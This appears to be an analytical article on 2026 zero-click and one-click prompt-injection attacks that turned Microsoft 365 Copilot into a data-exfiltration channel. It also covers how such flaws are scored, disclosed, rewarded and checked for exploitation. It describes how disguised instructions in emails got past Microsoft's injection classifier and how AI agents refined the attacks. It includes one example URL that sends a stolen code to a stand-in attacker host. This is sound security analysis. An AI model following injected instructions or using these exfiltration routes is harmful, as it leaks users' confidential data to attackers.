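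Varonis demonstrated the theft of an email's subject line. Subject lines are short but often contain sign-in codes, so an attacker who already knew the victim's password could have requested a code and tried to steal it before it expired. Varonis also lists salary data and acquisition plans as possible targets. Copilot could have searched for these if the victim was allowed to read them, but only a short extract would have fit in one image address. The attacker could choose what Copilot searched for, which EchoLeak's published version did not allow. Unlike EchoLeak, however, the attack required the victim to click.

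Microsoft fixed SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) on its own servers at the start of June, according to *New attack turned Microsoft 365 Copilot into 1-click data theft tool* (Toulas, 2026). Varonis stressed that the attack needed every step to work. Copilot had to treat the query as more than a search so that the attacker could control the answer, the software had to clean the answer too late to stop the image from loading, and Bing had to fetch the address for the code to reach the attacker. Microsoft could therefore have stopped SearchLeak by fixing any one of these weaknesses, but the others would have remained available for another attack.

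### August: ChatMate and CoSnitch

*Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 6 August 2026) showed that a malicious document could lead to an escape from the sandbox, the isolated environment in which Microsoft 365 Copilot runs code (CVE-2026-32193).

Later that month, Varonis published CoSnitch, an attack on Copilot Personal that could take data from a victim's connected Gmail, Google Drive and Calendar accounts after one click on a link. Breached.Company reports that Varonis reported the flaw to Microsoft in December 2025, that Microsoft fixed it on 18 August 2026, and that the company's enterprise assistant was unaffected.

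### ReLeak: one unread email, three exits

On 3 December 2026, Cato AI Labs published three attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot under the name ReLeak. The team had discovered EchoLeak when it was called Aim Labs. Its parent company, Aim Security, became part of the network security firm Cato Networks in September 2025 (Faisal, 2026, *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*). *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents the new attacks as a sequel to EchoLeak.

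All three attacks started with an email, as EchoLeak had, and the employee didn't have to open it. When the employee next asked Copilot a work question that made it retrieve the email, Copilot followed the instructions inside, collected confidential information the employee was allowed to see and sent it out. ReLeak fits the strict definition of zero-click because the employee didn't click or approve anything.

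Microsoft's XPIA classifier, its filter for injected instructions, did not stop any of the attacks. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* explains that Copilot resisted direct commands but followed instructions that looked like legitimate requests. Microsoft had changed its defences since EchoLeak, but disguising instructions in broadly the same way still worked.

The attacks differed in how the information left:

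| Exit | What contacted the attacker's server | CVE number | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| An image in Copilot's answer | A Bing server | CVE-2026-124115 | 15 November |
| A link in a file Copilot saved | A Microsoft server processing the file | CVE-2026-124132 | 11 November |
| Code that Copilot ran | The code sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | 17 September |

Cato reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August, so Microsoft took 28 to 50 days to fix the sandbox, at least 83 days to fix the saved files, and at least 87 days to fix the Bing image. It fixed all three on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. All three fixes took less than the 140 days between Rehberger's report of the font leak and its fix.

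### A link that nobody had to open

The leak through saved files was the least like earlier attacks on Copilot. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them in OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's services for storing and sharing files. Suppose an employee's mailbox contains the code for the company safe, DUNLIN-6042. The attacker's email makes Copilot save a document containing this link:

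`https://reports.example/source?ref=DUNLIN-6042`

No one had to open the document or click the link. Microsoft's servers process newly saved files in the background, and one of them requested the address while doing so. Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) reports that in Cato's tests these requests reached the attacker's server one to eight minutes after the chat ended.

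File services often do this background work, for example to make a thumbnail or prepare a file for search. Slack's link previews are similar, but a person who posts a link in Slack can usually see the preview appear. An employee who has finished a Copilot conversation has no reason to expect that a file from it is still being processed, or that closing the chat doesn't stop a leak.

Even a careful check of the links and images in Copilot's answer could not have prevented this, because the data was in the file. The CSP did not apply either, since the employee's browser was not involved in the request. The employer's network equipment would also have missed it, as it did with ShadowLeak, because the file and the server that processed it were both in Microsoft's cloud. The saved file might have helped an investigator, though, because it would still have contained the link with the stolen code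 unless someone deleted it. An image in a chat answer is easier to overlook.

This exit would also be hard for information-flow control to block. Only people entitled to read an employee's data can open that employee's OneDrive folder, so a rule that checks only the permitted readers would let Copilot save the file there. To catch the leak, the rule would have to treat the storage service as something that can contact outsiders, which the rule's designers might not know. FIDES could still have blocked the action under its trusted-action rule, because the decision to save the file came from an untrusted email, but only if the company treated saving a file as a consequential action.

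### Code that reached the internet

Microsoft 365 Copilot can write and run short Python programs, for instance to analyse a spreadsheet. It runs them in a sandbox so that a faulty or malicious program can't damage anything outside. In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, an article on the Russian security site SecurityLab, Antipov (2026) notes that Microsoft's documentation guarantees that these sandboxes have no incoming or outgoing network traffic. Cato's researchers broke through this isolation and had a program send confidential data directly to an outside server.

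The attack did not need an image, a link or another service to pass the data on. Code can also, in principle, send much more data than fits into a web address, so this was potentially the most serious of the three exits. That may be why Microsoft fixed it first.

The sandbox was supposed to block all traffic, a rule without the gaps that EchoLeak exploited in the link filter and CSP, but the software failed to enforce it. Even a deterministic defence depends on the program that carries it out. An administrator who read the documentation could reasonably have concluded that running code gave Copilot no way to communicate with the outside. Rubrik had also escaped from Copilot's sandbox that summer.

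Custom assistants that companies build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can also use this code feature. Antipov adds that nobody has confirmed whether the flaw affected these assistants.

### Why Bing could leak data again

In the image attack, Copilot put the stolen data in the address of a markdown image, the employee's browser loaded the image automatically, and a Bing server passed the data to the attacker. This attack should have been the easiest to anticipate, because SearchLeak had used Bing in the same way, and Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak about two months before Cato began sending its reports.

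Varonis did not say which of SearchLeak's weaknesses Microsoft had fixed. Microsoft may have stopped links from putting instructions into Enterprise Search, or cleaned the answers sooner, and left Bing unchanged. ReLeak would have got around either change. Its instructions came in an email instead of a link, and it used markdown, which Copilot's chat window normally turned into an image, so the image did not have to load before the code block was applied.

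Microsoft may also have stopped Bing's picture search from fetching an attacker's address, and Cato may have found a different Bing feature that would fetch it. Antipov calls the two channels similar, which is consistent with this. A large search engine fetches web addresses for many purposes, and the CSP allowed all of bing.com.

Under either explanation, the June fix stopped the attack that Varonis had reported but did not make Bing a safe destination for images from Copilot. Microsoft had good reason to stop a working attack quickly by fixing whichever part was easiest to fix. But attackers have countless ways to word an email or get instructions in front of Copilot, and far fewer servers that the browser trusts and that will contact an address the attacker supplies. Fixing how data gets out therefore protects against more attacks than fixing how instructions get in.

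Microsoft already had reason to expect this kind of exfiltration route, because EchoLeak had used Teams in a similar way. Varonis advised security teams to check such lists for any service that fetches user-supplied addresses. Customers can't change Copilot's list, so in practice only Microsoft could follow that advice.

It would have been hard to follow completely. Bing's picture search has to fetch addresses that strangers supply to be useful, and Copilot probably needs to show some pictures from Bing in its answers. Microsoft could serve those pictures from a separate domain that does nothing else, and allow only that domain. It could also check that the whole address is already public before loading an image, as OpenAI does. In his write-up of the Copirate attacks, Rehberger recommended such a check, which he thought Microsoft's assistants did not yet have. The check would have caught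 the Bing image, but it would have covered the saved files only if Microsoft's background servers used it too. It would not have affected a sandbox with an open connection.

Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak, Faisal reports. The Bing image is strong evidence for this, since it repeated an exit that Microsoft had already seen, and so is the classifier's failure to recognise any of the emails. The other two exits came from Copilot's ability to write files and run code, so they show Microsoft adding useful features faster than it could secure them, rather than failing to learn from EchoLeak. Cato sells protection for AI systems and has an interest in a bleak assessment, but researchers without such products have found the same underlying weakness.

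### AI agents as testers

Other AI agents helped Cato's researchers. According to Antipov, the agents wrote test cases, studied why Copilot refused them and adjusted the next tests, while people directed the work. Pixel Magazine describes a systematic search for weaknesses, which the team then refined into complete attacks.

This kind of work suits an agent because most attempts fail, as they did in the LLMail-Inject contest. An agent can reword an email hundreds of times without tiring as a person would, and can continue for as long as someone pays to run it. It can also learn from refusals by comparing many attempts, since small differences between them can reveal what triggered the filter.

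While working on the font leak, Rehberger asked Copilot itself to write a web page that used as many ways as possible to load external content. One of these, a background image, got past the preview's restrictions. Further work with Copilot turned up the font request, which worked in more of Microsoft's programs. Copilot supplied ordinary knowledge about web pages, and Rehberger recognised which parts mattered.

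The researchers behind CoSnitch also questioned Copilot about its own workings. Blake (2026) writes in *Microsoft Copilot Flaw Chain Lets Hackers Steal Data* that they manipulated it into revealing weaknesses that they then used in the attack. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* gives a similar account. Such answers can save a researcher from guessing, but they need to be tested because a model can invent details about its own software. Tenable and Radware had obtained similar help in 2025 by reading the reasoning that Gemini and ChatGPT displayed.

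These cases don't show that agents can find such leaks without expert guidance. People chose each target and judged which results were important, and Cato's team already knew Copilot well from its work on EchoLeak. But agents reduce the work of searching a large product for ways to send data out, and attackers can use the same method. Microsoft would have an advantage in running similar tests because it can read Copilot's source code and see every request its servers make. An outside tester of the saved-file leak had to wait up to eight minutes to learn whether an attempt had worked.

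## How vendors rate and reward these flaws, and whether they have been exploited

Microsoft scored the severity of EchoLeak at 9.3 out of 10, while NIST, the US standards institute, scored it at 7.5 in its National Vulnerability Database (NVD). Both used the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), in which 9.0 or more is critical, 7.0 to 8.9 is high and 4.0 to 6.9 is medium. Analysts have also disagreed about a later Copilot leak. Most of the disagreement is about whether the victim had to do anything and whether the damage spread beyond Copilot.

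### How CVSS counts a click

In version 3.1 of CVSS, an analyst answers eight questions about a flaw. A formula turns the answers into two scores, one for exploitability (how easily an attacker can use the flaw) and one for impact (how much harm it does).

One exploitability question concerns user interaction. *Artificial Intelligence Vulnerability Scoring System*, a proposal for scoring AI flaws that borrows the question from CVSS, defines it as whether anyone other than the attacker has to take part in the attack. The answer "none" is worth 0.85 and "required" is worth 0.62. If a stranger can easily use the flaw over the internet, exploitability without user interaction is

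8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 ≈ 3.89

With user interaction, the last factor becomes 0.62 and the result falls to about 2.84.

The score also depends on scope, which is whether a flaw in one component affects resources outside that component's security boundary. If it doesn't, CVSS adds exploitability and impact. If it does, CVSS uses a formula that gives a slightly higher impact value, then multiplies the sum by 1.08. In both cases, it rounds the result up to one decimal place, with a maximum of 10.

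The official record of EchoLeak, as reproduced by GCVE (2025), contains both sets of answers:

| | Microsoft | NVD |
|---|---|---|
| User interaction | None | None |
| Scope | Changed | Unchanged |
| Harm to confidentiality | High | High |
| Harm to integrity | Low | None |
| Exploitability | 3.9 | 3.9 |
| Impact | 4.7 | 3.6 |
| Score | 9.3 | 7.5 |

Neither Microsoft nor NVD counted the employee's question to Copilot as user interaction, although EchoLeak did nothing until somebody asked one. This is sensible, because asking questions is ordinary use of the assistant. A more literal reading would have counted the question and lowered Microsoft's score to 8.2 and NVD's to 6.5.

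The record doesn't include reasons for the two scope ratings, but both are defensible. Copilot already had permission to read the employee's mail and files, so NVD could treat them as part of the vulnerable component. Microsoft could treat the mailbox and file store as separate services with their own access rules, whose contents were exposed by a weakness in Copilot. On integrity, Microsoft's rating seems better, since the attacker's email made Copilot leave a source out of its answer.

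CVSS also limits the score for data theft. A flaw that only discloses data can score at most 8.6, even if a stranger can use it without a click and it exposes everything the victim can read. EchoLeak scored higher only because Microsoft also counted some harm to integrity. The Hacker News' *Microsoft Patches CVSS 10.0 Azure AI Foundry Flaw Enabling Unauthorized Privilege Escalation* (2026) lists another flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that scored 9.9. Unlike EchoLeak, it required the attacker to be an authorised user. But that user could gain extra privileges, so the limit for pure disclosure didn't apply.

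### "Critical" at 6.5

SearchLeak, the 2026 attack through Copilot's Enterprise Search, started when the victim clicked a link. According to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026), Microsoft scored it 6.5 and cited the required user interaction, while NVD scored it 7.5 and judged that the attack needed none. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-46401 · Microsoft · M365 Copilot+1* (2026) lists all the CVSS metric values behind the 7.5. Changing only the user interaction value lowers the total from 7.48 to 6.43, which CVSS rounds up to 6.5, so the disagreement over user interaction can account for the whole difference.

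Microsoft was right that SearchLeak requires a click, because Varonis itself presented it as a one-click attack. NVD may have had too little information when it rated the flaw. Positive Technologies dates the flaw's publication to 4 June, eleven days before Varonis explained the attack, and its short technical description doesn't mention a click.

Microsoft also labelled SearchLeak critical, as The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails, Files* (2026) reports. A CVSS score of 6.5 is only medium, but Microsoft's label comes from its own scale. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* reported that Microsoft had rated the flaw 10 out of 10, apparently from confusing the two scales.

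In the AI section of its severity scale, Microsoft rates prompt injections by their security impact. It rates an injection as critical if it lets an attacker steal another user's data with no user interaction, and gives "zero click" as an example. This description fits EchoLeak and ReLeak well, but it doesn't explain SearchLeak's critical rating, because Microsoft scored that flaw as requiring a click.

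Two other Copilot flaws show the same mismatch between label and score. STAR Labs' *Microsoft 365 Copilot's Business Chat* (2025) describes an information disclosure flaw that Microsoft called critical but that scored 7.5. According to Faisal, Microsoft also labels the ReLeak flaw in Copilot's code sandbox critical, although its score is 8.6.

Antipov reports that this score was at first 7.4. The formula gives 7.4 for a disclosure flaw with changed scope that requires user interaction, and it gives the later score if no interaction is required. Other combinations of answers could produce the same two scores, but a correction from one-click to zero-click would fit what Cato found. Antipov could not confirm public scores for the other two ReLeak flaws, whose CVE numbers were still marked "reserved" when Cato published, so their full records had not appeared.

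For ordinary software, companies use CVSS scores to decide which updates to install first. With Copilot they have nothing to install, so a score is useful mainly for deciding how urgently to look for signs of a past theft. CVSS is a rough guide for this because it doesn't measure how much a particular employee can read. EchoLeak, for example, has the same score whether the account belongs to a trainee or the finance director.

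### A CVE for a flaw that customers can't patch

Cloud companies used to publish a flaw in their own services only if customers had to do something about it. In *Toward greater transparency* (2024), the Microsoft Security Response Center announced that Microsoft would issue CVEs for critical flaws in its cloud services even when customers had no patch to install. Microsoft marks these records "exclusively-hosted-service" and lets administrators filter them out.

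The CVE programme, which runs the public catalogue of flaws, had just revised its rules. Under the new rules, a vendor "should" disclose a flaw if it could cause significant harm, or if others need to act on it or assess their own risk. Vendors are not required to do so.

Microsoft has since used the practice heavily. It published 18 cloud CVEs on 17 September 2026 alone, according to *Microsoft、Azure・Copilotなど18件の脆弱性を修正* (三村, 2026), an article on a Japanese security site. Four were disclosure flaws, three of them in Copilot products. Microsoft had already dealt with all 18 on its own servers.

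When a vendor fixes a flaw without issuing a CVE, customers may not learn that they were exposed. Suppose a law firm's staff used an assistant for a year before the vendor quietly fixed a leak like EchoLeak. The firm wouldn't know to search its old mail for suspicious messages, and by the time a researcher published the details, the logs it needed might be gone. It also couldn't tell clients about the risk or consider the flaw when deciding whether to renew the vendor's contract. OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak without informing even Radware, which had reported it, so customers depended on Radware to publish the details.

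Tenable had raised this concern in an earlier dispute, when one of its researchers complained that Microsoft had silently patched a flaw in its cloud, TechTarget reported. Bob Huber, Tenable's chief security officer, accepted that companies needed an agreed way to identify cloud flaws but was much more worried about whether vendors disclosed them at all.

Microsoft's policy largely addresses that complaint, but it guarantees CVEs only for critical flaws, and Microsoft decides which flaws are critical. Its first rating can be too low, as it was for Rehberger's invisible-character attack.

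A published CVE record can also lack detail. The record for EchoLeak describes the flaw in one sentence and links to Microsoft's advisory and Aim's page. It doesn't give the date when Copilot became vulnerable or list any signs of an attack that an administrator could look for. Customers could learn far more from Aim's report than from the CVE record.

Some of the tools built around CVEs also make little sense for a hosted service. EPSS, an automated forecast, estimates the probability that somebody will exploit a flaw in the next 30 days. In November 2026 it gave EchoLeak 7.2 percent, higher than about 94 percent of other flaws. That score probably reflected EchoLeak's fame, since Microsoft had fixed the flaw for every customer at once 18 months earlier and nobody could still have been running a vulnerable version.

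### What earns a bounty

Microsoft bases its rewards for prompt injections on the harm they cause. Its *Copilot Bounty Program*, which covers the consumer assistant, offers between $250 and $30,000. Reports that typically earn nothing include prompt injections with no security impact on anyone except the attacker, and attempts to extract the assistant's standing instructions. An injection that sends out another user's email may therefore qualify, but one that only makes Copilot ignore its rules in the attacker's own chat typically would not.

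This is a reasonable rule for a weakness that nobody knows how to remove. If every successful injection earned money, researchers could keep submitting rewordings of the same email, and Microsoft would pay repeatedly for a weakness it already acknowledges. Proof of stolen data is also easier to judge. *Measuring the Vulnerability Disclosure Policies of AI Vendors* (2025) notes that AI flaws often exploit probabilistic systems and fall outside traditional threat models, which makes them harder to classify, report and repair.

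The drawback is that a researcher who finds a reliable way past the XPIA classifier but no way to get data out may have little to gain by reporting it. Microsoft would then learn of the bypass only as part of a complete attack. Its rules also exclude types of flaw for which it is already investigating "broad mitigations", and researchers can't easily know in advance which those are.

The bounty for an attack with several steps depends partly on how Microsoft classifies it. For a critical flaw and a high-quality report, the consumer programme pays up to $8,000 for "inference manipulation", the category that includes prompt injection, and up to $12,000 for information disclosure. Server-side request forgery, the flaw that let Bing pass data on, can earn $20,000. A report that fits several categories gets only the highest award, so a researcher who finds such a chain earns the most by proving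 the request forgery, which encourages work on exfiltration channels.

Microsoft 365 Copilot has had a much narrower bounty programme, which ran from 17 February to 18 March 2026 and was open only to researchers taking part in a live hacking event. The top award for information disclosure was $8,000, though Microsoft may pay more at its discretion. This was less than the top award for the consumer assistant, although the workplace product can expose a company's files.

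Cato submitted its ReLeak reports four months after that programme closed. The reports may have qualified another way, because Microsoft now accepts more research outside its named programmes under its "In Scope By Default" policy. ITPro's *Microsoft forks out record-breaking sums with expanded bug bounty program* says the policy is part of the reason total payments rose from $17 million to more than $20 million in a year. The larger sum was shared among 562 researchers, an average of about $36,000 each, so even the highest listed award for a Copilot disclosure flaw is modest by Microsoft's standards.

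Microsoft's *Bounty Program Guidelines*, updated on 20 November 2026, require finders to keep a report confidential until Microsoft has fixed the flaw, and to withhold detailed exploit code for another 30 days. Microsoft fixed the last ReLeak flaw on 15 November, so these terms would have allowed a finder to describe it in outline on 3 December, as Cato did, but not to release detailed exploit code before 15 December.

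A researcher who sets Microsoft a deadline at any point loses the bounty. This rule gives Microsoft time to fix the flaw carefully, but it also removes the researcher's main way to speed up a slow fix. Under Microsoft's terms, a researcher who publishes before the fix, as PromptArmor did with Slack AI, could lose the payment and their place in the programme.

The guidelines allow one review of a disputed severity rating if the finder asks within 30 days, and Microsoft's second decision is final. Microsoft may also suspend people who send in many reports that no human has checked. This rule will probably matter more each year, because AI agents like those that helped Cato can produce such reports with very little effort.

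OpenAI made a similar distinction between injection and harm in 2024. It closed Rehberger's report about planting memories in ChatGPT but acted on his later report, which showed conversations being stolen.

### "No customers affected"

When vendors and researchers have announced these flaws, they have usually said that no customers were harmed. Microsoft reported that EchoLeak had affected no customers, and Slack said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. WinBuzzer's *Microsoft Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026) reported no public evidence of active exploitation when Varonis disclosed the attack.

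The assurance about ReLeak changed when the news reported it. Faisal's article opens by crediting Microsoft with saying that no customers were affected, but the body attributes a weaker statement to Cato, that it knows of no affected customers. Antipov also reports that Cato had no information about victims or real attacks on the day it published.

Cato is poorly placed to know whether these flaws have been exploited, because in each ReLeak attack a Microsoft computer contacted the attacker from outside any customer network that Cato could watch. Microsoft has the relevant logs, but they would be much more informative for some attacks than others.

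Exploitation is easiest to check for in the sandbox, because its programs were supposed to have no network access and any outgoing connection would have been suspicious. If Microsoft recorded connections from the sandbox and found none except Cato's, it could rule out that attack with some confidence for the period its logs cover. For the second attack, investigators could also look for the saved files.

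Data theft through Bing is much harder to detect. Bing's servers routinely fetch URLs supplied by strangers, so a theft would look like an ordinary image search. To find one, Microsoft would have to pick out the requests that began on a Copilot page and then check their URLs for company data, which an attacker could have encoded.

How much a clean search should reassure a customer depends on how likely it was to find a theft. Take an invented case in which there is a 10 percent chance that someone used a flaw, and call the chance that the logs would reveal it *d*. If the search finds nothing, the remaining chance is

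0.1 × (1 − *d*) / (0.1 × (1 − *d*) + 0.9)

The chance falls to about 1 percent if *d* is 90 percent, but only to about 8 percent if *d* is 20 percent, so in the second case the customer learns very little from the search. In these public assurances, no company gives a figure for *d* or says which logs it searched.

Official databases don't settle whether attackers have exploited these flaws either. The US cybersecurity agency CISA marked EchoLeak's exploitation as "none" on 14 June 2025, three days after the flaw became public, and that rating is still in the record. CISA also keeps a catalogue of flaws that attackers are known to have used. According to 三村, none of Microsoft's 18 September CVEs was in it three days after publication. But CISA adds a flaw only if organisations have a clear remedy to apply, so a flaw that a vendor fixes entirely on its own servers may never appear.

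Customers can do some checking themselves. Help Net Security's *Microsoft details AI prompt abuse techniques targeting AI assistants* describes a Microsoft playbook for finding suspicious activity in logged interactions with an assistant. The logs are most useful if they record which items the assistant retrieved as well as what it answered, because the email used in EchoLeak told Copilot not to mention that message. The email also stayed in the mailbox, so a company could have searched for it once Aim had described what to look for.

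### Attempts and thefts

Attempted attacks are much easier to detect than successful data theft. Microsoft's email filter, for instance, can count the messages it quarantines as injections, but that count would include researchers' tests and false alarms and miss every message that got past the filter. Even if an email reached a mailbox, the assistant might never have retrieved it, and if it did, the attacker still needed a working way to send the data out.

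Some injections have aims other than theft. Microsoft describes links with pre-filled prompts that plant instructions in an assistant's memory, and calls them a practical one-click attack because most major assistants accept such links. Reprompt and SearchLeak used the same entry point. A campaign using these links would therefore show that outsiders can get instructions into assistants on a large scale, but not that they had taken any data, since they may only want the assistant to recommend a product.

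An AI-generated entry in the OECD's monitor of AI incidents, *Slack AI Vulnerability Exposes Private Channel Data*, classes the Slack flaw as a plausible future harm because PromptArmor found it, and Slack patched it, before any documented damage. The flaw would get the same classification if someone had used it to steal data and nobody had noticed.

Government warnings don't establish whether criminals have exploited these flaws. The argument in the post from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre is based on how language models work, and it would hold whether or not any thefts had occurred. To confirm a theft, an investigator would need to link a hostile message to the answer that followed it, and that answer to a request that carried real data to an outsider. The public accounts of EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak document these links only in the researchers' own tests.

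Real thefts may have been rare while these flaws were open, because finding EchoLeak took Aim about three months and a criminal who wants a company's mail can often get it with an ordinary phishing page. A patient spy might still have thought the effort worthwhile, and would have had good reason to keep it secret.

### Who gains from a frightening report

Many of the firms that find these leaks sell protection against them. The page with Simonovich's ReLeak report also advertises Cato's security products for employees who use AI, for AI applications and for AI agents. Aim and Radware had similar commercial interests when they reported EchoLeak and ShadowLeak.

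There is little reason to doubt that the attacks worked, since the vendors changed their products in response. The researchers' commercial interest is more visible in how they describe the attacks. Ravia calls EchoLeak's technique a major advancement in how "threat actors" can weaponise AI, but only Ravia's colleagues are known to have used it. Varonis used the word "weapon" in the title of its SearchLeak report and called the attack chain critical, although Microsoft gave it a medium CVSS score.

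Vendors have an incentive to play down their flaws, which can lead to wording like Slack's "very limited and specific circumstances." But Microsoft hasn't done so consistently. It scored SearchLeak a point lower than NVD did, for a good reason, and scored EchoLeak almost two points higher than NVD did.
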